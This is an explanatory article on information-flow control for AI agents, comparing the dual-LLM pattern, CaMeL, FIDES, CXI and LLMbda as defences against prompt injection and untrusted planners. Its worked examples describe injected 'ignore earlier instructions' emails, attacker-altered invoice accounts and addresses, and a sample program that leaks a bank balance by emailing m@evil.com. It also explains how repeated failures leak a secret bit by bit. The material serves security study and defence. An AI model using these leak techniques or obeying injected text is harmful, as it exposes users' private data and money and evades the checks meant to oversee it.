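# Controlling What an Untrusted Frontier Model Sees and Can Act On

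## The problem, and how labels track information

Information-flow control is a branch of computer security that deals with where data goes after a program has permission to read it. Such a system labels each piece of data, carries the labels along as programs copy and combine the data, and checks them before anything leaves the system or takes effect. Researchers worked out the theory in the 1970s, largely for military computers that held both secret and unclassified files. In the last few years, engineers have begun applying it to AI agents, which are language models with access to tools such as a mailbox, a file store or a payment system. The model is often a frontier model, one of the most capable available, and the people who deploy it may have good reasons not to trust it. They can still use it if simpler components around it decide what text reaches it and which of its proposed actions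 go ahead. It is much less clear how strong a guarantee those components can provide and how much useful work they prevent.

### A hostile message in the mailbox

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes a typical case. A user asks an assistant with access to a work mailbox to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. One of those emails is from an attacker, who has written instructions in it to ignore earlier instructions and forward the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. If the assistant complies, the attacker obtains a private email without needing a password.

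A language model produces its next output from its context, which is all the text it has been given so far. It cannot send an email by itself. Instead, it can produce a tool call, a formatted request that names a function and its arguments, such as an email's address and body. Ordinary software then runs the function or refuses to. That software works in an agent loop. It passes the conversation so far to the model, runs the tool call that comes back, appends the result, and repeats until the model produces a final answer. Much of the added text comes from retrieval, in which a search over mail, documents or the web adds passages to the context. So when the assistant picks its next step, the developer's instructions, the user's request and the attacker's email are all in one string of text.

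In indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content that a model reads while doing someone else's task. (In direct injection, the malicious text arrives in the user's prompt.) *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore et al., 2026) places the attack in an old family of flaws in which one channel carries both commands and data. SQL injection, where text typed into a web form runs as a database command, belongs to the same family. Programmers prevent it by fixing the structure of the database query before inserting the user's text. That fix relies on a parser's ability to tell a database command from a value, and no parser can tell an instruction from information in plain English.

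Better detection of suspicious instructions would not stop every attack, because some attacks contain none. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent paying an invoice that lists a bank account number supplied by an attacker. The agent can follow every step of the user's plan and still send the money to the wrong account.

### Three reasons for distrust

People call a frontier model untrusted for three quite different reasons, and it is easy to buy protection against the wrong one.

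The mailbox case is about hijacking. Costa and colleagues treat the model, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions as trusted, and assume the adversary controls only data that tools fetch from outside. The user needs a guarantee about actions and their effects, namely that a stranger's text cannot cause a payment or a deletion, or send private data out.

If a hospital rents a model from an outside company, patient records leave the hospital's control as soon as they enter the model's context. Checking the model's tool calls is then too late, so the hospital has to check every query before it reaches the model. Costa and colleagues check only tool calls because they assume that adversaries cannot observe queries to the model, but they note that the same mechanism can also check queries when that assumption fails.

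A model might also pursue ends of its own, with no attacker involved. A guarantee against that has to hold for any output the model could produce, including outputs chosen to get around the checks. Girrens and Wang exclude alignment failures that arise independently of information flow from their threat model, and Costa and colleagues effectively do the same by trusting the model. Older computer security has a fairly close match in the Trojan horse, a program that does its advertised job but also does something else. *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (Sandhu, 1993) gives an example. Tom lets Dick, but not Harry, read a confidential file. Dick opens it in a text editor that Harry wrote, and the editor secretly makes a copy that Harry can read. Dick is honest and the permissions on Tom's file are correct, but they don't extend to the copy. Keeping such a program from leaking what it reads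 is called the confinement problem, and it is harder than stopping an attack sent in a stranger's email.

### The rules of the 1970s

Sandhu regards it as hardly practical to require that all software be free of Trojan horses. The alternative is to put the checks outside the program. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, set out the idea of a reference monitor, a mechanism that compares every access a program attempts with a list of what that program's user may do. Anderson gave it three requirements:

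- It must be tamper-proof, since a monitor that an attacker can alter protects nothing.
- The system must always invoke it. Any program that escapes the check becomes part of the security machinery, and someone then has to verify that program as well.
- It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing, because otherwise nobody can know that it works in all cases.

Anderson judged a commercial Honeywell system against these three conditions, and it failed all of them. Its hardware kept each program inside its own area of memory, but mostly stopped enforcing this while the operating system was acting on a user's behalf. The operating system and its supporting software contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, too many to verify, and testers had repeatedly broken into the system. A language model is also too large to test exhaustively, so although it may be a useful filter, it makes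 a poor monitor for another model. Narisetty and colleagues, who interpret the newer agent defences as reference monitors placed at the tool call, raise the same doubt about designs in which a language model writes the policy.

A monitor also needs rules to enforce. For secrecy the best-known ones go back to Bell and LaPadula (1973), in *Secure Computer Systems*. In Sandhu's version every running program s and every file o has a security level, written λ, and two conditions apply:

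- s may read o only if λ(s) ≥ λ(o);
- s may write o only if λ(s) ≤ λ(o).

The condition on writing guards against the Trojan horse by stopping a program running at the Secret level from writing an unclassified file. Harry's editor must run at Secret to open Tom's file, so it cannot create a copy that an unclassified user could read. The restriction applies to programs and not to people, because the model assumes that people will keep secrets out of an unclassified memo. The rules also only stop leaks from a higher level to a lower one, so they would not help Tom if Harry had a Secret clearance like the other two.

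Biba's model applies the same idea to integrity, or how far data deserves trust. It reverses the inequalities, so a program may not read data less trustworthy than itself or write to data more trustworthy than itself. Sandhu points out that there is no deep difference between the two models, since putting untrusted data at the top of the scale turns Biba's conditions into Bell and LaPadula's. One variant, which suits agents especially well, lets a program read untrustworthy data but lowers the program's own level when it does. Narisetty and colleagues describe an agent whose integrity drops after the model reads an untrusted web page, to a level at which it may not authorise a high-integrity action.

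Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, supplied the general theory. It starts from a set of security classes and a relation A → B, which means that information in class A may flow into class B. The relation has to be transitive. If data may move from A to B and from B to C, then it may move from A to C, since a program could otherwise do in two steps what the policy forbids in one. Denning then adds an operator for combining data. Its modern name is the join, written ⊔, and it has two properties:

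- A → A ⊔ B, and B → A ⊔ B;
- if A → C and B → C, then A ⊔ B → C.

Combined information is at least as restricted as each of its sources, and no more restricted than those sources require. Classes with this structure form a lattice. A system can keep a single label for a document drawn from fifty sources, because the document may go exactly where all fifty may go.

### Two joins worked through

In an agent, a source is a place, such as the tool that fetches mail, where data enters and receives its first label. A sink is a point where data has an effect, such as sending an email or writing a file. Taint tracking carries the labels from sources to sinks and joins them whenever data combines. A policy check runs just before the sink. It is a fixed rule in ordinary code that reads the labels and allows or blocks the tool call.

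Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article on building these checks into real products, has a good example for confidentiality. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. One message is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but has no right to see them yet. Each message's label is the set of people who may read it: {Alex, Priya} for the one and {Alex, Marco} for the other. A person may read a text based on both messages only if that person may read each of them, so the join is the intersection of the two sets:

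{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

The agent drafts a reply to Marco. The policy check compares the recipients with the permitted readers, finds that Marco is not in {Alex}, and stops the reply from going out automatically. Here the check catches an ordinary mistake by a helpful assistant, not an attack. If Priya had copied Marco, the first label would have been {Alex, Priya, Marco}, the join would have been {Alex, Marco}, and the check would have allowed the reply.

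Because the join is {Alex} whatever the draft says, the check also holds back harmless replies, such as one that only thanks Marco for writing. It would hold back a reply to Priya too, because the agent has already read Marco's message. If the agent had answered Priya before opening Marco's email, that reply would have passed.

For integrity the simplest lattice has two labels, trusted (T) and untrusted (U), and information may flow from T to U but not back. The joins are:

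T ⊔ T = T,  T ⊔ U = U,  U ⊔ U = U

If any input is untrusted, the result is untrusted too. A more detailed label lists everyone who could have written the data. The join of two such labels is their union, so the set of possible writers grows as data is combined, while the set of permitted readers shrinks.

In the project summary example, the user's request is labelled T, and the emails are labelled U because anyone can send one. The context that holds both is labelled T ⊔ U = U. If the policy permits consequential tool calls only from a trusted context, it blocks the forwarding even if the attacker's message completely deceives the model, because the check depends on the label and not on the model's judgement. But the policy also blocks the email to the manager, which the user asked for, because that is a consequential call from an untrusted context too.

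People therefore need a way to make exceptions. Endorsement deliberately raises the trust of data, as when a clerk confirms the account number on an invoice by telephone. Declassification deliberately widens who may read it, as when Alex looks over the draft and approves sending it to Marco. Sandhu notes that such steps fall outside the normal lattice framework because they break transitivity, since secret data may reach the public through a sanitising process but not directly. Exceptions are also an obvious target, because a rule offers little protection if an injected instruction can trigger its exception. Robust declassification addresses this by allowing data to be released only from a trusted context. A sample policy from Microsoft along these lines allows a post to a chat channel if the context is trusted or if every member may already read the content. Otherwise, it asks the user and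 lists the people who would gain access.

All of this assumes the initial labels are correct. Narisetty and colleagues point out that nearly every scheme treats the user's own input as trusted, even though a user can be tricked into pasting in a stranger's text. The labels are then wrong from the start, and even correct tracking will carry the error to the sink.

### Flows that copy nothing

Joins account for data that a program copies or combines. Information can also travel without any copying. Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, show this with a program of two statements, in which x is either 0 or 1:

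y := 1; if x = 0 then y := 0

At the end y equals x, although no statement copies x into y. An explicit flow passes information by copying data, and an implicit flow passes it through which action the program takes. Here the flow exists even when x is 1 and the second assignment never runs, because leaving y unchanged also reveals x. An agent can create an implicit flow too. Suppose an assistant reads a confidential email about a merger and decides whether to book a meeting room based on what it finds. Even if the booking contains no words from the email, anyone who can see the room calendar learns something about the email.

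Noninterference rules out both kinds of flow. SRI, the research institute whose computer scientists developed the theory, defines it to mean that none of the actions of one part of a system can affect what another part later sees. For example, if the assistant runs twice with the same request but different confidential emails in the mailbox, under noninterference an outsider sees exactly the same thing both times, including whether the meeting room is free.

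This standard is very strict for an agent. Costa and colleagues think it would come close to forbidding any tool call with a publicly visible effect once an earlier call may have read a secret. They control only explicit flows instead, and accept that someone who watches the sequence of tool calls may infer a limited amount about the secret.

Exact checking is impossible even for ordinary programs. Denning and Denning prove that no general procedure can decide whether some run of a program will produce a forbidden flow, because such a procedure would also solve the halting problem, the question of whether an arbitrary program ever stops. Their checker therefore rejects any program whose text specifies a forbidden flow, even when the code that specifies it could never run.

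### Why a language model is hard to track

With an ordinary program, the checker can read the code to see which variables a value is computed from. In the assignment c := a*2 + b, c is computed from a and b, so its label is the join of their labels. A secret variable d elsewhere in the program doesn't affect c's label.

In a language model, any token of the input (a word or piece of a word) may influence any token of the output, and no line of code records which ones did. A reply may repeat a figure from one email, take its tone from another, and leave something out because of a third. For programs whose behaviour is unknown, Sandhu advises assuming that information flows wherever it could. Costa and colleagues apply the same rule to models by giving the output the join of the labels of everything in the context, including the tool descriptions.

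The rule is safe but imprecise. If a context contains forty trusted messages and one untrusted message, the whole context is untrusted. Every tool call the model then proposes is also untrusted, even if the untrusted message didn't influence it. That message stays in the conversation on the next turn, so the label stays too. Over a long task the label can only become more restrictive, which eventually leads to label creep, where restrictive labels spread until they block ordinary work.

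Costa and colleagues mention a gentler method, from Siddiqui and colleagues, which identifies the messages that influenced a response, then regenerates the response from those alone. The new response can carry a more permissive label because the model produced it without seeing the rest. Some implicit flow presumably remains, since the choice of which messages to keep depended on all of them. The more common approach is to keep untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. A planner picks the tool calls, and a separate, quarantined model reads the stranger's email and has no tools to misuse.

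## How planner-and-reader designs separate instructions from data

The idea of splitting an agent into a planner and a reader comes from a blog post, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023). Willison wanted an assistant that could, for example, read an email and add the action items to a to-do list. Nobody knew how to make a model reliably ignore instructions hidden in such an email, so Willison looked for a design that would be fairly safe even if that problem was never solved. Most later designs, including Google DeepMind's CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES, build on this split. They guard against text hijacking the model that reads it, and they assume the planner is honest as long as it reads only trusted text.

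### Passing text by reference

Between Willison's planner, which the post calls the privileged model, and the quarantined model is a controller, a piece of ordinary software that runs the tool calls and stores the results. The planner never receives the stored text, only a name for it. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the work goes like this:

1. The planner requests the latest email and asks the controller to store it as $VAR1.
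2. The controller fetches the email and stores it, without showing it to the planner.
3. The planner requests a summary of $VAR1 from the quarantined model.
4. The controller replaces the name with the real text, passes it to the quarantined model, and stores the answer as $VAR2.
5. The planner writes a reply that contains the name $VAR2, and the controller fills in the summary on the user's screen.

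Suppose the email contains an instruction to delete the whole mailbox. The quarantined model may try to follow it, but the worst it can do is write a bad summary. The planner can delete emails, but it never receives the instruction.

The quarantined model's summary of an email is as dangerous as the email itself, because a hijacked model can copy the attack into its output. Willison therefore insists that free text from the quarantined model must never reach the planner, even after passing through several further prompts. The one exception is when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of categories, because ordinary code can check that the output is exactly one of them before passing it on.

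Willison called the solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and one careless feature that passes untrusted text to the planner undoes all the protection. An attacker can also use the summary to manipulate the user, for instance into pasting private data into a website. Displaying an image can leak data if the image's address contains that data, so the controller also has to restrict links and images.

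The CaMeL paper identifies a more basic flaw in the pattern, which Willison (2025) readily accepts in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting. The meeting notes contain both the document's name and Bob's email address. The planner decides to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document and send it. Nothing in the notes can change those steps. But the quarantined model extracts the address, and an attacker who can write in the notes can make it return a different one, so that the document goes to the attacker. The pattern protects the control flow (which actions run, and in what order) but not the data flow (which values those actions receive).

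### A program in place of a conversation

CaMeL, published in 2025, keeps the two models and adds labels to cover the data flow. Its name is short for "capabilities for machine learning". The planner reads the user's request and writes out the whole task as a short program before any model has read untrusted data. For Bob's document, the program might look like this:

```
notes   = find_meeting_notes("Bob")
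name    = ask_reader("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
file    = fetch_document(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=file)
```

Here `ask_reader` stands for a call to the quarantined model. The real system uses a restricted form of Python, because language models already write Python well. A custom interpreter runs the program one operation at a time and records which values each new value came from. These dependencies are easy to see in a program. For example, `address` depends on `notes`, but a subject line that the planner took from the user's request would not depend on `notes`.

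Every value carries two tags, which *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes as its sources (where it came from) and its readers (who may see it). Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy check written as a Python function. The function takes the tool, the arguments and their tags, and returns a decision to allow or deny the call, with a reason.

A sensible policy for `send_email` would require the recipient to come from a trusted source. The address fails that test because it came from the notes, so the system stops and asks the user, even if nobody tampered with the notes and the address really is Bob's. A policy could instead check whether the recipient is permitted to read `file`. The system would then send Bob the document without asking if he already had access to it, and would still keep it from a stranger. This check would not detect that an attacker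 had changed `name`, so Bob might receive the wrong document from among those he may read.

The program may contain branches, so it can react to data that the planner never sees. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) gives the example of a program that sends an email only if an account balance exceeds a threshold. Sending the email would be an implicit flow of information about the balance. CaMeL's interpreter treats a call inside the branch as dependent on the balance and blocks the email. CaMeL therefore catches some flows that FIDES does not, although the paper also reports leaks that CaMeL misses.

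The interpreter can do this only because the language is small. According to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), agents using it cannot define their own functions or use recursion. That paper's system instead lets agents write ordinary Scala, a general-purpose programming language, and the compiler checks before the code runs that code handling classified data cannot print it, save it or send it over the network. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) finds even the restricted Python too loose, because types can change as the program runs and errors can redirect its execution. It recommends a special-purpose language with bounded loops and with the labels built into its types.

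CaMeL also checks each tool call only when the program reaches it, so a long task may use many model calls and then fail at the last step. CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, translates the program into a finite-state machine and examines every path through it before any tool runs. It can then enforce rules about a whole run, such as requiring the agent to resolve or escalate every security incident before it finishes. If a path breaks a rule, the checker returns that path and the planner tries to repair the program. The checker assumes that a loop may stop or continue after any pass, so it sometimes rejects a safe program.

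The split also helps if the hospital rents a model from an outside company, because CaMeL's planner sees only the user's request and its provider never receives the records that the tools return. The quarantined model does see them, but extracting a date or an address is easier than planning, so a small model on the hospital's own machines may be good enough. The user still has to keep confidential details out of the request. Someone also has to write and maintain the policies, and Willison worries that users who are asked for approval too often will start to approve everything.

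### Hiding only what would taint the context

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built, keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the planner chooses one tool call at a time. It puts a label on every message, tool call, argument and stored item. The developer's instructions and the user's request normally start as trusted and public, the least restrictive label. When a call passes the policy check, its result receives the join

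ℓ(result) = ℓ(call) ⊔ ℓ(arguments) ⊔ ℓ(stored data that the tool read)

Anything the tool writes gets the same label, so an attacker's text stays untrusted even if the agent saves it to a file and reads it back later.

With nothing more than this, the first untrusted email would taint the context and block most of what follows. Willison's remedy was to hide all outside content behind variables. FIDES hides less. When a result arrives, ordinary code compares its label ℓ with the label c of the current context:

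- if ℓ ⊑ c, the result is no more restricted than the context, so the planner sees it in full;
- otherwise, the code stores the result in a new variable, and the planner sees only the variable's name.

Either way, the context's label stays the same. The planner is as well protected as if everything were hidden, and it has more information to use. If the context is already untrusted, further untrusted results appear in full because hiding them would add no protection.

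The code applies the rule to each part of a structured result separately. One test task was to change a user's password if a recent bank transaction looked suspicious. The planner could read the amounts and dates, which were trusted, but the subject line of one transaction was untrusted and stayed in a variable. The planner judged a large payment suspicious from its amount alone and changed the password. This followed the rule, because nothing untrusted had influenced the decision, but the planner decided without seeing the subject line, which a person would probably have read.

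A planner can also pass a variable as an argument without reading its content. Just before the call, the code replaces the variable's name with the stored content and its label, so a single call can have parts with different labels. For example, in a message to a colleague, the decision to send and the recipient may be trusted, while the body is an untrusted summary of a web page.

Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for checking such calls. The first covers consequential actions and requires the call and all its arguments to be labelled trusted. The second covers outgoing data and requires everyone who can read the channel to be allowed to read the data. This second policy is the rule that blocked Alex's reply to Marco. On its own, it does not prevent hijacking, but it limits what data a hijacked agent can leak.

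If applied strictly, the first policy would make hidden variables almost useless for consequential actions, because any untrusted argument would block the call. Costa and colleagues therefore relaxed it in their tests, so that it ignored the arguments and checked only the context in which the planner chose the call. They used this version for bank transfers, hotel bookings and password changes. Emails and new calendar events only had to satisfy either this version or the policy on outgoing data.

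The relaxed policy reintroduces the dual-LLM pattern's vulnerability. In the invoice attack that Girrens and Wang describe, the quarantined model would copy the attacker's account number into a variable. The planner would have read nothing untrusted, so the check would allow the transfer. FIDES can express a better rule that requires a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted message body. However, someone has to decide which arguments must be trusted for every tool.

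### When the next step depends on the data

Some tasks need the same steps whatever the data turn out to contain. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls, with one final response, solves it in every case. More exactly, let D be the set of possible states of the data, such as all the mailboxes the user might have. For each state d in D, let S(d) be the set of sequences that solve the task. The task is data-independent if

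⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅, taken over all d in D,

and data-dependent if no sequence works for every d.

Forwarding the top three emails to a colleague is data-independent, because the planner can pass them on by name without reading them. Sending a summary of the three is also data-independent, provided a quarantined model writes the summary. Creating a calendar event only if one of the three contains a meeting request is data-dependent, because the right sequence of actions depends on what the emails say.

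A planner that sees only variable names cannot do this reliably. The two mailboxes look the same to it, so any fixed choice is wrong for one of them. A more capable model would not help, because it would lack the same information.

Data-dependent tasks are common in some kinds of work. In AgentDojo, a benchmark that tests agents in simulated workplaces, Costa and colleagues classed 5% of the office tasks and 10% of the travel tasks as data-dependent. The share was about 44% for banking and 43% for the workplace chat program Slack, where users often ask the agent to read something and act on it.

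CaMeL can handle the meeting request with a branch in the program, since the interpreter can test a value that the planner never sees. But the planner has to think of every branch in advance, which is hard if the user asks for whatever is due today on a to-do list to be completed. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an agent that fixes reported bugs. Strangers write the bug reports, so a strict design hides the reports from the planner, which then has to guess what is broken in a repository of perhaps thousands of files.

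FIDES deals with this by revealing very little. The planner can ask a quarantined model a question and specify the type of the answer, such as a Boolean (true or false) or a choice from a list. Constrained decoding then prevents the model from producing anything else. A hijacked model can still give the wrong answer, but it cannot add instructions. The answer goes into a new variable, which the planner can open with a separate tool, `inspect`.

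The meeting request takes five calls:

| Call | Result | Untrusted content the planner has seen |
|---|---|---|
| Read the top three emails | The emails, stored in variable A | None |
| Ask the quarantined model whether A contains a meeting request, answer type Boolean | The answer, stored in variable B | None |
| Inspect B | The word "true" | One Boolean |
| Ask the quarantined model to extract the event details from A | Date, time and participants, stored in variable C | One Boolean |
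| Create an event from C | A new calendar entry | One Boolean |

If B turns out to be false, the planner stops after the third call.

FIDES adds the answer's type to its label. It ranks types by how much information they can carry, from a Boolean to a choice from a list to free text. When the planner inspects B, the context's label becomes (untrusted, Boolean). A strict policy would block the event's creation because the context is no longer trusted, so the policy has to make an exception for contexts whose only untrusted content is a Boolean. This exception is a form of endorsement. If the planner had opened the emails, the label would be (untrusted, text), and the exception would not apply. The policy must also ignore the label on C, since the event details come directly from a stranger's email.

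An attacker who sends one of the three emails can still cause a meeting to appear and choose its time and guests, which is partly what the user asked for. The attacker cannot make the planner forward the mailbox, because no text from the email ever reaches the planner.

### How much a typed answer can carry

An answer with n possible values carries at most log₂(n) bits of information. A Boolean carries 1 bit, and a choice between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding an email carries log₂(3), or about 1.6 bits. Over several answers the possibilities multiply, so the bits add up:

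log₂(n₁ × n₂ × … × nₖ) = log₂(n₁) + log₂(n₂) + … + log₂(nₖ)

Three yes/no answers have eight possible combinations and carry 3 bits. Twenty have 1,048,576, which is enough to identify any six-digit login code.

FIDES does not keep this running total. The join of two Boolean labels is again a Boolean label, so the context's label shows no more exposure after a hundred answers than after one. *Trident* (2026), a later design that meters the influence of untrusted data, also notes that FIDES records the capacity of each answer but has no budget across answers. An honest planner has little reason to ask twenty questions about a login code. But if a user asks an agent to deal with each of two hundred unread emails, an attacker who sent forty of them controls at least forty answers.

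It is less clear what an attacker could do with those forty bits. They could in principle encode five characters of text, but the planner would have to decode them and treat the result as an instruction. Jacob and colleagues limit the length of lists in their own system to rule out such attacks. They let the quarantined model return whole numbers, decimals, Booleans and choices from a list the developer has vetted. In their shopping agent, the quarantined model turns each product review into two whole numbers, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for how relevant the review is. The first runs from 0 to 10, so it carries about 3.5 bits.

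One argument for these designs is that a number cannot contain a command because a command needs free text. That seems right for a score out of ten. The argument is weaker if numbers can be any size, because a long enough number can encode any message, and safety depends on the planner never decoding it. Short text is riskier still because it can be read as English. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) discusses a proposal to let a coding agent see function names from untrusted software if they are no longer than 30 characters. Thirty letters, digits and underscores can carry nearly 180 bits. An attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which fits the limit and hints at a command that deletes files.

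Capacity is also a poor measure of how much harm an answer can do. In one FIDES example, a user asks the agent to look up a Paris hotel and book it if its rating is above 4. The planner sees only the word "true" from the untrusted reviews and ratings, and makes the reservation. That single bit determines whether the agent spends the user's money, and a fake review might be enough to flip it. Jacob and colleagues place such false information outside their threat model because it misleads the agent without giving it a new task.

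In their tests, Costa and colleagues set a policy that allows hotel bookings only in a trusted context. Under that policy, even the word "true" would block the reservation unless Booleans were exempt. As Garby and colleagues point out, the FIDES evaluation left this exemption switched off, so its benchmark results do not show how well typed answers work in practice.

### Tying provenance to the action

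CaMeL and FIDES control what the planner reads before it chooses an action. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, July 2026) presents CXI, a system that focuses on the action about to run. CXI is designed for cases where the planner may have read hostile text and may propose a harmful action. It requires every part of the proposal that matters to have its own source of authority.

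A coding agent that reads the log of a failed test needs it to find out which file failed. But text in the log should not be able to determine which database tool the agent uses, mark a change as approved or trigger a second attempt. An attacker who can write to the log would want to use it for all three. Santos-Grueiro calls it authority laundering when something that should only count as evidence gains the power to authorise an action.

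A CXI policy therefore classifies every field of every tool call. Fields that shape the effect, such as the tool, the recipient, the file path and the approval status, are protected. Writing W for text an attacker could influence, X for a protected field and D for a typed release, the rule is

W ↛ X unless W → D → X

A typed release is a value that trusted code has checked and approved for one field. If the log names a file and the code confirms that the path is valid in the repository, the path may fill only the file-path field. FIDES limits how much information an answer can carry, and a single bit meaning "approved" carries very little. CXI limits where an answer can go, so it would reject that bit in the approval field if it came from the log. The agent may still quote the log in a comment, but if another agent later reads that comment, the quoted text counts as untrusted again.

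CXI tracks influence as well as copying. Even if a tool's name is copied exactly from a trusted list, CXI treats the choice of tool as untrusted if something in the log led the model to pick it. With an open-weight model, whose internals the operator can control, the software can block the model's attention to untrusted text while the model generates a protected field. The operator has no such access to a rented model, so CXI falls back on the division of labour in Willison's pattern, where one component reads the raw text and separate writers fill the protected fields from trusted data and typed releases.

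Some arguments are programs, such as database commands or changes to source code. A bug fix has to draw on the bug report, so a rule that rejected everything with an untrusted origin would reject every fix. Instead, trusted code works out exactly what such an argument would do, for example which files it would change, how, and starting from which version of the repository. A validator, which is also trusted code, then decides whether that effect is acceptable.

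The final check has six steps:

1. Convert the proposed action into a standard record, called a manifest.
2. Check the authority behind each protected field.
3. Check that a validator has approved the exact effect.
4. Check that the action may happen at this point, which covers retries and repeats.
5. Use up a single-use permission tied to the manifest.
6. Run the action.

The permission is tied to a digest, a short code computed from the whole manifest. If the manifest changes after the checks, the digest no longer matches and the action fails. An attacker therefore cannot get a harmless change approved and then swap in a different one, or reuse the approval in another repository.

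CaMeL derives its program from the user's request alone, while CXI can take a proposal from a planner that has read the bug report. That suits coding agents, whose work mostly depends on the data they read, but CXI's policies take a lot of careful writing. The policies for 24 kinds of action covered 149 fields, 85 of them protected, and a first audit found 18 faults, half of them serious. Some policies accepted approval in free text, and others did not cover arguments that could change a system's behaviour. The validators also have to be good, because CXI will carry out any harmful change that one of them approves.

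## What has been proved, and under which assumptions

The policies in FIDES and CaMeL are useful only if the labels they use are correct. Several groups have therefore tried to prove that an agent's labels account for every information flow that matters. They disagree about which flows matter, and each proof covers only part of a working agent.

### Explicit secrecy in FIDES

Costa and colleagues show that label tracking like that used in FIDES can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. The property is defined over the agent's data store, which holds everything its tools can read or change, such as mail, files and calendars. Each item is either public or secret. The notation d₁ ≈ d₂ means that two stores have the same public items, though their secrets may differ.

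Now take a path, meaning the steps an agent actually follows from some starting store. Each tool call on the path may change the store, and g stands for the combined change. Queries to the model leave the store as it was. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every path it can follow from a store d₁,

d₁ ≈ d₂ implies g(d₁) ≈ g(d₂).

In other words, if the same steps ran on a store with different secrets, the public items would come out the same.

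In the example of the merger email and the meeting room, suppose the email confirms the merger in d₁ and denies it in d₂. The path "read the email, book room 4 on Friday" adds the same booking to either store, so it satisfies the definition. But the agent follows that path only from d₁ and books nothing from d₂, so the booking reveals the merger. A path that posted the email on a public page would violate the definition, because the page would differ between the two stores.

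A single decision reveals little, but a program could leak a whole secret by going through it bit by bit and making one of two harmless calls for each bit. Garby and colleagues raise this objection to explicit secrecy, which they say is weakest where a program can easily turn data into decisions and so leak it quickly. Costa and colleagues accept the risk because full noninterference would block too much ordinary work. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on smartphones, make the same compromise.

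FIDES is in some ways stricter than the property. The formal definition treats a call's arguments as fixed text so, read strictly, it misses a secret that the model reads in one call and writes into the arguments of the next. The labels do catch this, because whatever the model writes carries the label of the context it has read, and the policy on outgoing data checks that label. The same check could also stop the room booking, but not a revealing call that takes no arguments.

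The proof also treats the model as deterministic, always giving the same reply to the same conversation. Real models usually sample their replies at random. This probably matters little for explicit secrecy, which ignores the choice of path, but a great deal for noninterference, because a secret might raise the chance of some visible action from 10% to 90% without making it certain.

### Two leaks in CaMeL

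CaMeL tries to track decisions as well as copies, but it has no comparable theorem, and its designers left a formal treatment to later work. Garby and colleagues found two ways around its tracking. One needs only a short program like this:

```
1  tmp = True
2  rich = True
3  if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
4  if tmp: rich = False
5  if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret, and everything else starts out public.

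| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | `tmp` becomes False and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays True and public |
| 4 | Skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | `rich` becomes False and stays public |
| 5 | The email goes out | No email |

CaMeL raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment to that variable. When the secret balance is high, the program skips line 4, so no assignment runs and `rich` keeps its public label. In both cases `rich` shows whether the balance is high, and the interpreter lets the email through. J. S. Fenton described this problem in 1974.

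An attacker's email cannot add these lines, because CaMeL's planner writes the program before any model reads untrusted data. An honest planner would write them only by accident, so the flaw matters most if the planner might be dishonest.

The standard remedy is to stop any program that tries to change a public variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. Here the program would stop at line 3 if the balance were high. No email would go out, but someone who noticed that it had stopped would still learn one bit about the balance.

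Most systems tolerate a leak of that size, but in CaMeL an attacker could repeat it. The interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop, and if an attempt fails, the planner gets an error and writes a new program. Each attempt starts with clean labels, even though the planner has received information from the previous one.

Suppose the balance is a whole number of dollars from 0 to 1,048,575. A program could attempt a forbidden call only if the balance exceeds 524,287. The planner then learns which half of the range contains the balance from whether the policy blocks a call. Each further attempt can halve the remaining range, so the planner knows the exact balance after 20 attempts. CaMeL censors error messages to limit the information that passes between attempts, but the planner can presumably still tell that an attempt failed.

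Garby and colleagues also mention a simpler bug, in which inserting an untrusted value into text makes the result trusted. This flaw may matter the most of the three in practice, since planners routinely build text from stored values.

### LLMbda: labels on every value

In response, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents, and proved theorems about every program in it. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions that computer scientists often use for proofs. The main addition is a conversation with a language model, which a program controls with three commands:

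- `@e` sends the prompt `e` and returns the model's reply, which may be data or code.
- `fork e` runs `e` on a copy of the conversation, then goes back to the original.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

In one example, a program explains the format of British postcodes in a first prompt and then forks the conversation for each of three addresses. The model gets the explanation every time but never sees one address while working on another.

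A program can also fork the conversation and clear the copy before sending a prompt. The model then sees only that prompt, and its reply never enters the main conversation. This gives the same isolation as Willison's quarantined model. FIDES and CaMeL build that isolation into their architecture, whereas an LLMbda programmer can write it as an ordinary function and use it where needed.

Every value has a label. The conversation's label is the join of the labels of all the messages the program has sent. The program also keeps a program-counter label, which records what data influenced the decision to reach its current position. Code in the model's reply runs under the conversation's label, so if the model has read an untrusted web page, everything its code produces is untrusted.

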